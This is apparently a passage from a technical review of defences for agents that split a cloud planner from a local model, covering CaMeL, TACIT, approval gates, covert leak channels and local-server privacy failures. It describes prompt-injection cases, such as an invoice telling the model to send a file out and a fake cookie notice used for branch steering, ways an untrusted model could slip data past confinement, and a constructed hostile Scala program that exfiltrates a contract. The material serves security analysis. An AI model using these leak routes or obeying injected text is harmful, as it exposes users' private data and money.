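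The experiment was about injection, but the same step would break confidentiality even without an attacker. If the notification agent's planner were a cloud model, its provider would receive the applicants' details as soon as the coordinator put them in the message.

Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed the problem by giving messages between agents two parts. One part holds instructions, and the interpreter keeps anything derived from a tool's output out of it. The other holds labelled values that the receiving agent's program can use but its planner can't read. Across 949 attack trials with each of five models, attacks succeeded on average 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL on each agent separately and 0% with the two-part messages. GPT-5.5 resisted every attack even without CaMeL, so the trials can't show what CaMeL adds for that model. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that stronger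 attacks might still succeed against it. They also ran CaMeL without any security policies, so the results don't measure how well policies stop a program from sending private data to the wrong place.

### What CaMeL costs

A planner that can't see the data needs an exact description of what each tool returns, which ordinary tool documentation often leaves out. Peters-Gill and colleagues added these descriptions before testing CaMeL on 112 tasks from AssetOpsBench, a benchmark in which a coordinator delegates professional tasks to four specialised agents. CaMeL still lowered the completion rate by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models. Stronger models seem to cope better with planning without seeing the data, as the average loss for the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Fable 5, was 13.4 points.

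The loss can be larger if the environment is hard to predict. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. The plans for computer use averaged 213 lines of code and 40 branches, compared with about 52 lines and four branches for AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking and travel tasks. About half of the steps in the computer-use plans were fallbacks that never ran. With larger closed models, the agent kept at most 57% of its ordinary performance.

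CaMeL also takes more tokens and time. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that it used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an unprotected agent for the median AgentDojo task with GPT-4o. *AttriGuard* (2026), which presents a rival defence, tested agents under attack with two models. CaMeL averaged 165 seconds per task with one and 105 with the other, roughly ten times as long as without protection. *ToolFence* (2026) attributes CaMeL's slowness to its many stages: writing the program, interpreting it, rewriting it after errors and calling the quarantined model. The split design needs most of these stages anyway, so taint tracking may account for only a small part of the delay.

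### Static and runtime tracking compared

TACIT analyses the code before it runs, while CaMeL tracks data while the program runs. An interpreter may therefore detect a forbidden call only after earlier steps, such as a payment to Kristin, have already been carried out.

Static checking also lets programs use more of the programming language. CaMeL's Python has no user-defined or recursive functions. Odersky and colleagues argue that allowing them while still providing guarantees before the program runs would require analysing which functions could be called at each point in the program, and that the work this takes grows exponentially with the program's size in the worst case. TACIT avoids this analysis because each function's type lists the capabilities the function can use.

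Runtime tracking can make finer decisions because it has the actual values. TACIT either wraps a message or doesn't, and only a trusted library function can send a wrapped message to anybody. An interpreter with reader labels can let the program quote Kristin's own messages back to her but block the same text from going to her landlord. Odersky and colleagues consider the approaches complementary and suggest adding runtime checks to TACIT's library functions, such as limits on how often a program can perform an action.

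They also tested TACIT on AgentDojo and compared the results with CaMeL's published scores for the same models. The table shows the percentage of tasks completed.

| Model | System | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 52.8 | 53.8 | 48.6 | 1.4 |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 56.9 | 50.5 | 40.0 | 64.3 |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 62.5 | 81.4 | 68.6 | 74.3 |
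| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 59.0 | 52.9 | 47.6 | 68.6 |

The score of 1.4% makes sense only as a result under attack. AgentDojo pairs 20 travel tasks with seven attacker goals, for 140 combinations, and 1.4% is two out of 140. If the agent had attempted each of the 20 tasks once without an attack, every success would have added five percentage points. The other scores also fit this reading.

That doesn't explain why CaMeL did so badly with Gemini on these tasks, and Odersky and colleagues don't explain it either. Gemini completed 64.3% of the tasks with TACIT, and CaMeL completed 74.3% with o4-mini-high, so the cause can't be the tasks or taint tracking in general. The most likely explanation is a fault in how Gemini and CaMeL worked together, such as one coding error repeated in nearly every program. CaMeL's score with Gemini is best left out of any comparison between the two approaches.

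Odersky and colleagues call the remaining scores comparable, which is generous to TACIT. With o4-mini-high, CaMeL led in all four domains, by more than 28 points on workspace tasks and 21 on Slack tasks. With Gemini, each system led in some domains. The two teams ran their tests separately with different prompts and software, so the gaps may have little to do with the difference between types and labels. Still, the scores are no evidence that static checking makes an agent more useful.

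In the security tests, each system had one successful attack in 1,926 trials. In TACIT's case, the agent booked the correct hotel and then quoted reviews that contained the attacker's recommendation of another hotel, which AgentDojo's text-matching test counted as a successful attack. AgentDojo measures resistance to injected instructions, so neither system's score shows whether it can keep private data from a hostile planner.

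### Harm without a leak

A program can keep every private word from the cloud model and still empty the user's bank account. Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, give a definition that covers such cases. Let *T*<sub>q</sub> be the smallest set of actions needed to carry out request *q*. An agent oversteps if it takes any action *a* such that

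*a* ∉ *T*<sub>q</sub>.

An action includes its arguments. For the grocery request, *T*<sub>q</sub> contains a payment of $34.50 to Kristin, so a payment of $60 or a second payment of $34.50 oversteps. But nobody has a list of *T*<sub>q</sub> in advance, because finding the right amount is part of the agent's job.

SEAgent, the system that Ji and colleagues built, therefore uses more general rules. It gives each tool, agent and database security attributes and records in a graph how information flows between them. Rules about paths through the graph determine whether the system blocks an action, asks the user or lets it proceed. One of their test settings is a smart home in which guests can leave messages and the agent can open the front door. A rule can stop a guest's message from leading to a door command. The same method doesn't help with Kristin's $60, because the user wants her messages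 to determine the payment.

Labels can't catch a wrong value that comes from the correct source. If the local model picks the wrong number from Kristin's texts, that number has the same origin as the correct one. The broker can limit the damage with ordinary rules, such as capping the amount and allowing only one payment per request.

False information can also make a benign program do harm, even if it contains no instructions. Kim and colleagues give the example of a user who asks an agent to search for news and email a summary to someone. If an attacker's page is among the results, a phishing link may end up in an email that the user appears to have written. In a related attack, which Foerster and colleagues call branch steering, the attacker's data makes the program take a harmful branch that the planner wrote for legitimate use. In their tests, an advertisement disguised as a cookie notice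 got the agent to click through to the attacker's website. Similarly, an attacker's invoice marked "overdue" could trigger a payment from a program that pays overdue invoices straight away.

Private data may also go to someone who is on the list of permitted recipients but shouldn't receive that data. If the user has two contacts named Kristin, a program may send one of them medical results meant for the other. Reader labels will prevent this, but only if somebody has recorded which Kristin may read the results. Few people keep such records for their own email, although a company may already have them in its access settings for shared documents.

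Deletions are easier to contain than payments. The user's software can let the program work on a copy of a folder and show the user what has changed before replacing the original. Odersky and colleagues mention GoEX, an agent runtime that supports undoing actions. But no software on the user's side can unsend an email or recover money that a stranger has already withdrawn.

Outside commands can cause any of these harms, and neither CaMeL's interpreter nor TACIT's compiler can track what happens inside them. Odersky and colleagues suggest permitting only safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`. Including `sbt` is questionable because this tool for building Scala software runs code from the project's own build files. A program that can edit those files and then start `sbt` can run any code, limited only by the operating-system sandbox.

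### Approving exact actions

The user's software can ask for approval before an action that can't be undone. The approval has to refer to the exact action, because otherwise an attacker may change the action between approval and execution.

In *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents*, Jing (2026) built and measured a system that does this for commands on a Windows computer. The agent proposes an action. A separate policy gate uses fixed rules to allow it, refuse it or ask a person, and treats silence as a refusal. An executor carries out only what the gate has approved, and an auditor reviews the records later. The agent can't change the gate, its rules or the records.

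The gate calculates a digest of the file to be run. A digest is a short fingerprint that changes if any byte of the file changes. If *H* is the digest function and *a* the approved file, the executor runs a file *a*′ only if

*H*(*a*′) = *H*(*a*)

and nobody has used the approval before.

Jing added both conditions after tests showed the system needed them. An early version checked only the description of an action, and an attacker who swapped the file after approval deleted a decoy file in two of seven trials. After the fix, none of the seven attempts worked. With a second check of the file just before execution, the system blocked 90.3% of tampering and reuse attacks, up from 61.3%. Another version let an agent use an approval twice. Making approvals single-use raised the blocking rate for reused approvals from 77.8% to 100%.

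The main test had 117 dangerous commands in disguised forms and 54 legitimate tasks.

| Controls | Dangerous commands let through (%) | Legitimate tasks refused (%) |
|---|---|---|
| None | 98.3 | 0 |
| Rules applied to the command's text | 43.6 | 0 |
| Full approval system | 30.8 | 0 |
| Full system with a final file check | 30.8 | 0 |
| The same with an operating-system sandbox | 7.7 | 11.1 |

The sandbox accounts for the last large improvement. It restricts what a command can do however the command is written, whereas rules about text miss many of the ways to write the same command. The sandbox also accounts for all the refusals of legitimate tasks. The gate permitted work in some folders that the sandbox didn't let the agent write to, so coordinating the two better might have avoided some of these refusals.

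As an alternative to outside controls, Jing asked three models to follow a written instruction to seek approval before doing anything dangerous. On a smaller sample of disguised commands, Claude Opus 5 let through 89.8%, DeepSeek V4.1 Flash 94.9% and GPT-6 Astra 100%. In these figures, as in the table, a request for approval counts as granted, so they overstate the risk for a system with an attentive user. They are still good evidence that telling a model to ask first is no substitute for a gate it can't bypass.

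The 7.7% comes from a simulation of the sandbox. When Jing ran a related set of commands against the real one, five of 66 (7.6%) had an effect, but they weren't the five that the simulation had predicted, so the close agreement is partly luck. One of the five was a true escape: the sandbox blocked writing outside the work folder but let the agent delete a file on another disk. The sandbox was still clearly useful, since in 88 paired trials, 45 commands ran only when it was off and none ran only when it was on. The study has a single author and used one computer, so the percentages may not carry over to other systems.

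This kind of approval suits the split design because the user is allowed to see private data that the cloud model is not. Before paying Kristin, the broker could show "Pay Kristin $34.50, note: Groceries" on the user's screen and bind the approval to that account, amount and note. The broker has to write this description itself from the real arguments, because a hostile program could describe a transfer to an accomplice as a grocery payment. If a program pays Kristin and then crashes, the next program needs a new approval to pay her because each approval works only once, and the user has a chance to notice the duplicate.

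This works only if people read what they approve, and Willison expected that they wouldn't. Tallam and Miller propose asking for approval less often. Their scheme lets an agent read unrestricted data without approval, requires a quick confirmation when untrusted data affects a change to the user's own files, and keeps the strictest approval for irreversible steps such as emails and bank transfers. Jing didn't test human approvers, so the study doesn't show how many users would notice $60 on the screen instead of $34.50.

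## What error messages and results send back to the cloud model

If the user notices the $60 and refuses the payment, the agent needs a better program. To write one, the cloud model needs some information about what went wrong, and the explanation is in Kristin's messages. The same problem arises when a program crashes, or when a later step depends on an earlier result, such as whether a clinic has written to offer an appointment or to ask for more tests.

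Any reply from the user's side that depends on private data is a return channel. It threatens confidentiality because it reveals information about that data to the cloud model, and integrity because a stranger may have written some of the text it carries.

Accidental leaks are easy to produce. In this constructed example, a program tries to read the amount straight from Kristin's last message:

```python
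owed = float(messages[-1]["message"])
```

If the message isn't a bare number, Python stops with an error such as this:

```
ValueError: could not convert string to float:
'Groceries were 34.50. Hope the scan results are good news!'
```

Python quotes the text to help the programmer, who can usually see the data anyway. Here the programmer is the cloud model, so the device uploads the amount along with a clue about the user's health. This weakness is well known outside AI. *Towards Secure Logging* (2026) links it to CWE-209, the standard catalogue entry for error messages that contain sensitive information, and adds that error traces can expose internal names and library versions. Printed output carries the same risk. According to *How Your Credentials Are Leaked by LLM Agent Skills* (2026), agent frameworks put whatever a program prints into the model's context, including passwords a developer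 printed while debugging.

### The confinement problem

*A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) posed the problem of confining a borrowed program. Typically, a customer runs someone else's service on private data, and the service's owner may have written it to send the data back. In the split design, the user is the customer and the cloud model is the owner.

Some of the channels Lampson described are storage that another program can read later. A sandbox with no network connection and a temporary scratch folder closes most of these. Others are legitimate outputs, such as a service's bill, in which the service's dishonest owner can encode information about the customer. A crash report is similar to the bill because the agent needs it. The rest are covert channels, which nobody intended to carry information. Lampson doubted that anyone could rigorously identify every channel in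 a moderately complex system.

Noninterference, which Goguen and Meseguer formulated in 1982, would require that the private data make no difference to what the cloud model receives. An agent that sends truthful crash reports can't meet this standard if the data affect whether a program crashes. *Nonmalleable Progress Leakage* (2025) calls noninterference too restrictive for practical use and builds on a long line of work that permits declassification, the deliberate release of some information. A designer who allows declassification has to decide how much information to release and who controls the release.

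### How much a reply can carry

Suppose the cloud model receives *k* replies during a task, and trusted software on the user's side limits each reply to one of *m* values. There are at most *m*<sup>*k*</sup> possible sequences of replies. If *R* is the sequence and nothing else the cloud model receives depends on the private data *D*, then

*I*(*D*; *R* | *q*) ≤ *H*(*R*) ≤ log₂(*m*<sup>*k*</sup>) = *k* log₂ *m*.

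Each reply is one of eight codes, so it carries at most 3 bits, and five replies carry at most 15 bits. This limit still holds if the cloud model chooses each new program after reading the earlier replies. It also holds if a program is written to leak data, because the program can control which of the eight codes is returned but can't add new ones.

The eight values have to include success. If the device sends nothing after a successful run, that silence also counts as a value, because the cloud model can infer from it that the run succeeded.

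| What the cloud model receives | Most it can carry |
|---|---|
| A result in free text | About 8 bits per character, so 8,000 bits for 1,000 characters |
| An error trace in free text | The same, up to any length limit |
| One of eight codes, up to five times | 15 bits |
| The number of programs needed, up to five | 2.6 bits |
| Success or failure of one program | 1 bit |
| Running time | No fixed limit, as it depends on how precisely the provider can measure |

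The figure of 2.6 bits is log₂ 6, because the agent can succeed on any of five attempts or fail on all of them.

Fifteen bits can distinguish 32,768 possibilities, which is enough to reveal a four-digit PIN, since there are only 10,000 of those. A random 128-bit key would still be secure after one task, but nine tasks could reveal all of it. A user who cares about the total leaked therefore needs a limit that carries over between tasks.

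*L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) describes a design for such a limit. L3M is an agent runtime from Amazon, and its published version doesn't yet include the limit. For each kind of private information, such as payroll data, the runtime would count the bytes an agent has read and the bytes it has sent since reading any. The leak can't exceed the smaller total. If an agent reads 64 private bytes and then sends two 50-byte messages, it has leaked at most 64 bytes.

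The total for reading relies on the data-processing inequality, a theorem that processing data can't create new information about its source. If the private data reach the output only through the program's internal state, then

*I*(data; output) ≤ *I*(data; state).

The inequality limits what even free-text error traces can reveal, though the limit is seldom useful. If a program has read only one bill, its error trace can include the whole bill but nothing else from the mailbox. Letting programs open fewer files therefore reduces how much private data any crash report can expose.

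Counting the bits that went out doesn't show what they reveal, and a single bit can reveal a diagnosis. FIDES, a label-tracking system similar to CaMeL, has an option that lets values with few possibilities, such as true or false, pass its security checks because their influence is limited. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) raise the related objection that someone reviewing a run can't tell whether such a value is the release the designer intended or a real leak that looks the same.

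### Time and termination

The 15-bit bound covers what the replies contain but not when they arrive. A provider can measure how long a crash report takes to come back. If a program runs longer when a letter mentions a divorce, the provider can infer the divorce from the delay, even if the report always contains the same code. A program that never finishes can also reveal something, because the provider receives no reply.

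Most formal guarantees leave this gap open. The usual property is termination-insensitive noninterference, which compares only runs that finish. *Generalizing Permissive-Upgrade in Dynamic Information Flow Analysis* (2015) explains that this allows a leak of one bit when an observer sees only a program's final state, and possibly more when the program produces output while it runs. Garby and colleagues gave a computer-checked proof of a version of the property for agents that write and run code. Their version compares probabilities because a language model can respond differently to the same prompt.

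Garby and colleagues show how a leak of one bit per run can accumulate. CaMeL's interpreter tracks private data, but it runs inside an ordinary Python loop that retries after a failure, and nothing tracks the loop. Whether the security policy blocked an attempt can depend on a secret, so an attacker who can keep rerunning the program can learn the whole secret one bit at a time. A split agent that requests a new program after each crash has the same kind of loop, so its retry limit affects privacy as well as cost.

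The user's software can bound the information that timing leaks by replying only at fixed times. Suppose it sends each reply only at one, two, four or eight minutes after the program starts, and stops any program still running at eight minutes. The delay then adds two bits to each three-bit code, so five replies carry at most 25 bits. This makes replies slower. A crash after two seconds is not reported until the one-minute mark, and five such crashes take at least five minutes.

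### What the AppWorld programs sent back

The agent in the AppWorld experiment returned ordinary Python error traces. Radovič and colleagues examined the 2,917 exceptions from all their runs on the challenge tasks and found messages, notes or file contents in 12 of them, or 0.4%. Most exceptions carried coarser information, such as a timestamp the program couldn't parse or the fact that a particular file didn't exist.

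At that rate, a user whose programs crashed five times a day would upload a fragment of private text about once every seven weeks. The estimate rests on only twelve cases, so allowing only for chance, the true rate could be anywhere from about 0.2% to 0.7%. Real mailboxes are also messier than AppWorld's simulated ones, so programs may fail on them in different ways.

The 0.4% rate measures accidental leaks, since the Qwen models that wrote these programs were trying to complete the tasks and had not been asked to leak anything. A program written to leak can raise an error containing any text it has read, so one report could hold Kristin's entire conversation, and the model writing the program could set the rate. The measured rate is fairly reassuring for a user who worries mainly about what an honest model's provider happens to receive, but it is no evidence of safety against a hostile cloud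 model. Radovič and colleagues write that what leaves the device "should be guaranteed rather than incidental".

### Instructions in the reply

Suppose a stranger emails an invoice that has a sentence where the amount should be, saying that the way to fix this error is to send the file to a certain address. When Python can't convert that sentence to a number, the error trace includes it, and the trace goes to the cloud model to be fixed. The cloud model could then follow the stranger's instruction even though it never reads the mailbox.

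Fixed codes prevent this because the user's software defines all of them. The stranger can still influence which code the cloud model receives, for example by making the invoice unreadable, but can't write the message.

Hu and colleagues' Twin Agent system allows a little free text. Its Explore Agent reads untrusted content but can't carry out privileged actions. The Safe Agent carries out those actions and gets information about the content only through short hints from the Explore Agent. The Explore Agent also sees what the Safe Agent has done so far, so a hint needs to supply only what is missing for the next step. Software shortens or blocks hints that exceed a length limit, and a language model screens each one for injected instructions.

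| Benchmark and model | Agent | Tasks completed (%) | Successful attacks (%) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Software bugs, GPT-5.2 | No defence | 61.2 | 97.0 |
| Software bugs, GPT-5.2 | Separate agents, no hints | 0.0 | 0.0 |
| Software bugs, GPT-5.2 | Hints of up to 100 characters | 62.5 | 0.0 |
| AgentDojo, Gemini 2.5 Flash | No defence | 61.9 | 41.5 |
| AgentDojo, Gemini 2.5 Flash | CaMeL | 30.9 | 0.0 |
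| AgentDojo, Gemini 2.5 Flash | Hints of up to 200 characters | 62.9 | 0.1 |

CaMeL's score is a little low because Hu and colleagues cut its retries from ten to three to save compute. They say CaMeL scored about 35% in its original paper.

A hint of 100 characters was evidently enough for fixing bugs, but the Safe Agent could read the code and run commands, and the bug report was the only thing it couldn't read. A cloud model with no access to a user's files would need much more information from its hints. AgentDojo is closer to that case because every tool's output was withheld. Twin Agent did about as well overall as the undefended agent, but it scored 66.7% on the Slack tasks, compared with 90.5% for the undefended agent.

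These results are good evidence that a planner can work with very little text. They are weaker evidence that it can work with very little private information, because the system limits a hint's length but not its subject. At eight bits per character, a 200-character hint could carry 1,600 bits, and the Safe Agent can receive a new hint at every step. A single hint has ample room for "Kristin says groceries were $34.50". Short messages help more with integrity than with confidentiality, because attacks on the strongest models tend to need long injections, while many secrets are short.

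Hu and colleagues also tried an attack designed for Twin Agent. They hid text in the bug report telling the Explore Agent to copy a prepared message into its hint, and it always complied in single-step tests. Over complete tasks, the Safe Agent carried out the malicious action in 11 of 232 cases (4.7%). It never did so in 55 reruns of those cases, so the successes seem to have been partly luck. Hu and colleagues acknowledge that their design has no formal guarantee.

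The copied messages suggest a risk in the split design. If the local model reads a stranger's email and then writes free text to the cloud model, the stranger may be able to dictate that text.

### Repairing programs with less feedback

Fixed error codes are the simplest defence, but they can be too vague to help. The device in the AppWorld experiment chose among four labels for its "not found" errors, so each label carried at most two bits. Even when the cloud model also received the error trace, its next program often failed in the same way.

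A code could instead combine the type of error with the line number where the program stopped. The cloud model wrote the program, so it can interpret both. With 20 error types and 100 lines, there are 2,000 possible codes, so each code carries 11 bits and five replies carry 55. Such a code would probably be enough for the cloud model to fix a misused function, and it wouldn't reveal that Kristin had sent the amount by email.

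TACIT can completely hide errors in private computations from the cloud model by wrapping them like any other private data. The user can still read the errors on the secure output channel, but the cloud model doesn't receive them, so somebody or something on the user's side has to repair the faults.

The cloud model could also test its programs on invented data, as researchers do with OpenSAFELY's dummy medical records. If the invented messages and bills aren't based on the user's own, the cloud model can read complete error traces without learning anything about the user. Such tests would catch many wrong field names and type errors before the program opened a real file. They would help less with the unpredictable ways people write about money. Radovič and colleagues didn't test this method.

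If the local model repairs the program itself, as they suggest, nothing needs to go back to the cloud model. But a model small enough for a phone then has to debug a program it probably couldn't have written. Its repairs also need the same checks as the original program, since text in the mailbox may have influenced them. And if the local model can't fix the program and sends a request for help, the request reveals to the cloud model that this user's data caused an unusual problem.

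The local model could also rewrite the error trace in general terms, which Radovič and colleagues plan to try. But *MNC* (2026), which proposes a protocol for messages between agents, warns that a message without words such as "medical" or "legal" can still reveal the private reason through the pattern that remains. For example, a provider could guess that "no file found for the appointments every third Tuesday" refers to chemotherapy. PlanTwin's sanitised outputs carry a similar risk. If *MNC*'s rules allow no version of a message, the system can do the work privately, send nothing or ask the user.

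To guide the cloud model's later steps, the local model can choose from a list of options instead of writing an explanation. In Eisenach and colleagues' design, an agent with network access but no private data lists *N* options, and an agent with the private data but no network access replies with the number of one option. The reply carries at most log₂ *N* bits, however much the second agent has read. This limit holds only if the recipient can understand the options without help from the private side. Any private text in the options counts as a separate disclosure.

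In the clinic example, the cloud model could write three follow-up programs in advance: one to book the appointment, one to arrange the tests and one to do nothing. Telling the cloud model which program was chosen would reveal up to 1.6 bits, which might be exactly what the user wanted to hide. But if all three programs are on the device, the local model can choose among them and the device doesn't need to reply. This makes the program longer, and much of it never runs.

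### Releasing information on purpose

When none of this is enough, the user can agree to release some information. *Agent libOS* (2026) notes that researchers classify release policies by what information goes out, who may release it, where the release happens and when. In its system, each approval works only once, for an exact text, sender and destination. *Agent libOS* doesn't claim noninterference, and its system can't control what the recipient does with the text.

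Control over the release is a particular problem in the split design because the untrusted program controls when it crashes and what the error contains. It can therefore choose what the user's software will ask permission to send. *Nonmalleable Progress Leakage* argues that systems mixing secrets with untrusted code must restrict who can influence the content and timing of a release. At a minimum, the user's software should write the permission request itself, as the broker does for payments, and show the exact text.

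Prompt Flow Integrity, the system from Kim and colleagues, has a similar approval step. Its planner receives labels such as `#DATA0` in place of untrusted text. If the planner needs to read the text to decide what to do next, the user first sees the content, its source and its intended use. The system is meant to stop injected instructions, so the user then decides whether to trust the text. With a cloud model, the user also has to decide whether the provider may have the text, since they could easily trust a letter from their own clinic but want to keep it private.

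Kim and colleagues recognise that frequent alerts make an agent harder to use, so their system lets the user choose to always or never trust a source. Choosing "always" is risky for privacy because it would release the clinic's future letters before the user had read them.

Willison expected people to approve requests without reading them, and Eisenach and colleagues cite a finding that users approve about 93% of Claude Code's permission prompts. Review would work especially badly for crash reports, because at the rate in the AppWorld experiment only one in 243 would contain private text, and a user would probably stop reading the reports long before reaching it.

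The user's software could send only error codes by default and ask for approval when the cloud model needs the full error text. It could also search that text for passages copied from private files and highlight them. This should catch most accidents, such as the Python error that quoted Kristin's message, but it wouldn't catch a program that disguised the text first.

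## What has to be true of the local model

The designs described so far guard against a cloud model that misbehaves, but they assume that the local model works as intended. The local model reads Kristin's messages, the clinic's letters and the crash reports that are too private to upload. Calling it "trusted" means only that it is allowed to read them. For the protection to work, the software that runs the model has to keep prompts private, and no data can carry over from one call to the next. The model also has to answer accurately, even when a stranger has written part of a document to mislead it. Its weights have to come from somebody who hasn't trained it to misbehave. Any one of these assumptions can fail while the others hold.

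### The software that runs the model

A model's weights are a file of numbers. Running the model requires a serving system, which loads the file, accepts prompts, does the calculations and returns the text. In *The Illusion of Local Privacy*, Ibrahim, Ikram and Salama (2026) tested how well such systems keep prompts private. Most of their experiments were on llama.cpp, a widely used engine for running models, but they also tested two consumer applications, LM Studio and Ollama.

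The experiment used four open models with 4 to 14 billion parameters and put a random identifier in each test prompt. If an identifier later turned up in memory, in a file or in another client's output, it showed which prompt had leaked.

Prompts stayed in memory long after the model had answered. A single request left 13 or 14 readable copies. In a longer test, twelve users sent prompts to the same server one after another, and the researchers recovered text from 11 of them. The server makes copies as it unpacks the request, fits it into the model's prompt format and moves it to larger blocks of memory, and it releases the old blocks without overwriting them. A patch that erased some of the copies cut the recovered text from 10.8 MB to 3.4 MB, but that text still included prompts from 11 of the 12 users. Running part of the model on a graphics card didn't solve the problem either. After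 the researchers stopped the server, they found no identifiers in the memory they examined, so restarting it after a sensitive task is a simple precaution.

An attacker needs a process running under the user's own account to read this memory. Ordinary malware with that access can usually open the mailbox directly, so it gains little from the leftover prompts. The cloud model's program could gain more, because the user may have given it only a single folder. If it runs under the same account without a sandbox, it might be able to search the server's memory for documents from earlier tasks.

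With its default settings, the tested version of LM Studio also wrote full prompts to a log file, where Ibrahim and colleagues found them days later. Changing one setting and restarting the application stopped this. The researchers found no saved prompts in Ollama's files. Such a log can expose private data even without an attack. If the user's backup service copies the log to online storage, private emails leave the machine. A later program could also read the log as an ordinary file, because TACIT wraps only the contents of folders marked as classified.

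The most serious failure was in llama.cpp's feature for saving and restoring conversations, which the operator has to turn on. The server checked that a client had a valid key, but not that the saved conversation belonged to that client. One client restored another's conversation in all 200 trials. When asked to continue the conversation, the model repeated the other client's secret in 126 of them. Gemma and Qwen did so in all 50 of their trials, and Phi-4 in only one.

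Response times can also leak information about one client's prompts to another, even if no conversations are saved. The server caches its processing of recent prompts, so it responds faster to a new prompt that begins the same way. Qwen3.5 9B took 47 milliseconds to start answering when the server had already processed the opening and 1,150 milliseconds when it hadn't. A client can guess how somebody else's prompt began and test the guess by timing the response. In the reported measurements, this distinguished the two cases perfectly, even over a real internet connection.

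These two leaks matter in the split design, even when only one person uses the model on a laptop, because the untrusted program also sends requests to the server. If the program can contact the server directly, it may be able to restore or probe the prompts of other tasks. The trusted function that sends questions to the model should therefore be the server's only client. It should keep the server's key private, give the program no way to restore conversations, and either turn off the shared cache or clear it between tasks.

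The local model's server also has to be closed to the public internet. On 4 July 2026, Ibrahim and colleagues used a search engine for internet-connected devices and counted 32,723 Ollama servers that anyone could reach. Some owners may have intended this, but a user who exposed a server by mistake would be giving the public access to a private model server.

### Using a whole agent as the local model

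A user could also give the local role to a complete agent running on the same machine. The agent could look for the right document itself, but it would add much more software to the trusted part of the system.

*Local LLM Agents as Vulnerable Runtimes* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2026) studies the source code of OpenClaw, an agent that people install on their own computers. OpenClaw can run commands, open files, control a browser, send messages and use stored passwords. The project published 602 security advisories between 31 January and 15 May 2026. The researchers recovered the vulnerable code for 446 of them, of which reviewers had rated 12 critical and 134 high.

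The largest group, 77 advisories, concerned bypassing an authorisation check. Another 31 covered faults that let a crafted file path reach outside the permitted folder, and 30 covered faults that let an attacker run commands. Some of the faults would matter even if the model behaved perfectly. In one case, OpenClaw put the name of the working folder straight into the model's instructions, so anyone who could name the folder could add an instruction.

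Standard scanning tools missed most of these faults. Zhang and colleagues wrote scanning rules based on the earlier advisories and tested them on 217 later ones. The scanner Semgrep detected 21.7% of the later advisories by itself and 66.8% with the new rules, while CodeQL went from 13.8% to 75.1%. The scoring was generous, since any warning in a file that the fix changed counted as a detection. The new rules also produced many false alarms. When Zhang and colleagues checked 50 warnings about the current code, only six were correct.

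The number of advisories partly reflects how many people were looking for faults, and the study covers only one agent, so the study doesn't show that OpenClaw is worse than its competitors. The more general problem is that every part of such an agent runs with all of the user's privileges, as OpenSSH did before Provos and colleagues divided it. A function that sends one prompt to a model and returns one value needs no shell, browser or stored passwords. Limiting the local side to such a function avoids most of the faults in the audit, although the function still has to build prompts and handle errors safely.

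### No memory between calls

Both `slm` and TACIT's `chat` assume that each answer depends only on the current call. If call *i* has the question *p*ᵢ and the data *x*ᵢ, and *r*ᵢ stands for the model's fresh random choices, the answer should be

*y*ᵢ = *f*(*p*ᵢ, *x*ᵢ, *r*ᵢ).

A server that retains something from earlier calls has a state *s*ᵢ as well:

*y*ᵢ = *f*(*p*ᵢ, *x*ᵢ, *s*ᵢ, *r*ᵢ), with *s*ᵢ₊₁ = *g*(*s*ᵢ, *p*ᵢ, *x*ᵢ).

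The data from the first call can then affect the answer to the second. This would defeat TACIT's wrapper, because `chat` also has a version that takes ordinary text and returns ordinary text. In this constructed example, a hostile program uses both versions:

```scala
val contract = readClassified("contracts/acme.txt")
chat("Remember this document.", contract)
println(chat("Repeat the last document.", ""))
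```

The second call contains no wrapped data, so its answer is an ordinary string, and `println` sends it to the cloud model. If the server starts a new conversation for each call, the local model has no document to repeat, but if the server continues the same conversation, the cloud model receives the contract.

The compiler accepts the program whether or not the local model is stateless. A function's type limits what its Scala code can do with the program's capabilities, but the model runs in a separate process, often written in another language, which the compiler never examines. Odersky and colleagues therefore leave it to whoever sets up the server to ensure statelessness, and the type of `chat` only records that promise.

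They discuss a similar promise for a library class that stores a function's results to avoid computing them twice. Storing results breaks safe mode's rules, but a programmer may still mark the class as safe after checking that the function always returns the same result for the same input, because callers then can't tell from the results whether they were stored. A model server's prompt cache is harder to justify this way. It should leave the answers essentially unchanged, but Ibrahim and colleagues' measurements show that callers can detect it from the delay.

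Taint tracking also depends on the server keeping nothing between calls. Suppose the first call reads a letter from the clinic and the second reads Kristin's messages. The interpreter labels the second answer as coming only from Kristin's messages, so the program may send it to her. If the server has kept the letter, the answer could include part of it, and the label wouldn't show that.

The person running the server can test for this by planting a random identifier in one call and searching for it in later answers, much as Ibrahim and colleagues did. The test should also search the separate field in which some models return their reasoning, because Qwen and Phi-4 sometimes put recovered secrets there instead of in the answer. Such a test can detect data carried over between calls, but it can't prove that this will never happen. Starting a new server process for each task gives stronger protection,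 but it requires reloading several gigabytes of weights each time.

### No tools or network access

The type of `chat` also can't show whether the local model has tools. If the server lets the local model search the web, it could respond to a question such as "Find out what this patient's symptoms mean" by putting the symptoms in a search query, even though neither the cloud model nor the program sent anything.

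The user's software can turn off the local model's tools, but an update may change that setting. It is safer to run the model's server in a sandbox that blocks its network access and to pass questions and answers through a pipe. A company with a shared model server can't block all network access, but a firewall can limit the server to replying to the company's own machines.

### Hostile text from two sides

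Anyone who can email the user can put text in front of the local model. Developers have tried training models to ignore instructions in such text, or marking and filtering the text before the model reads it. These defences often do well against known attacks and worse against adaptive ones, in which the attacker designs the text to get past the defence. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) cites Nasr and colleagues (2025), whose adaptive attacks defeated twelve recent defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks.

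Later results, including Hu and colleagues' attack on their own Twin Agent system, also give little reason to rely on the model that reads the documents. *Confused ChatGPT* (2026) argues that adding a second language model as a checker only makes a successful attack less likely, because hostile text can manipulate the checker too.

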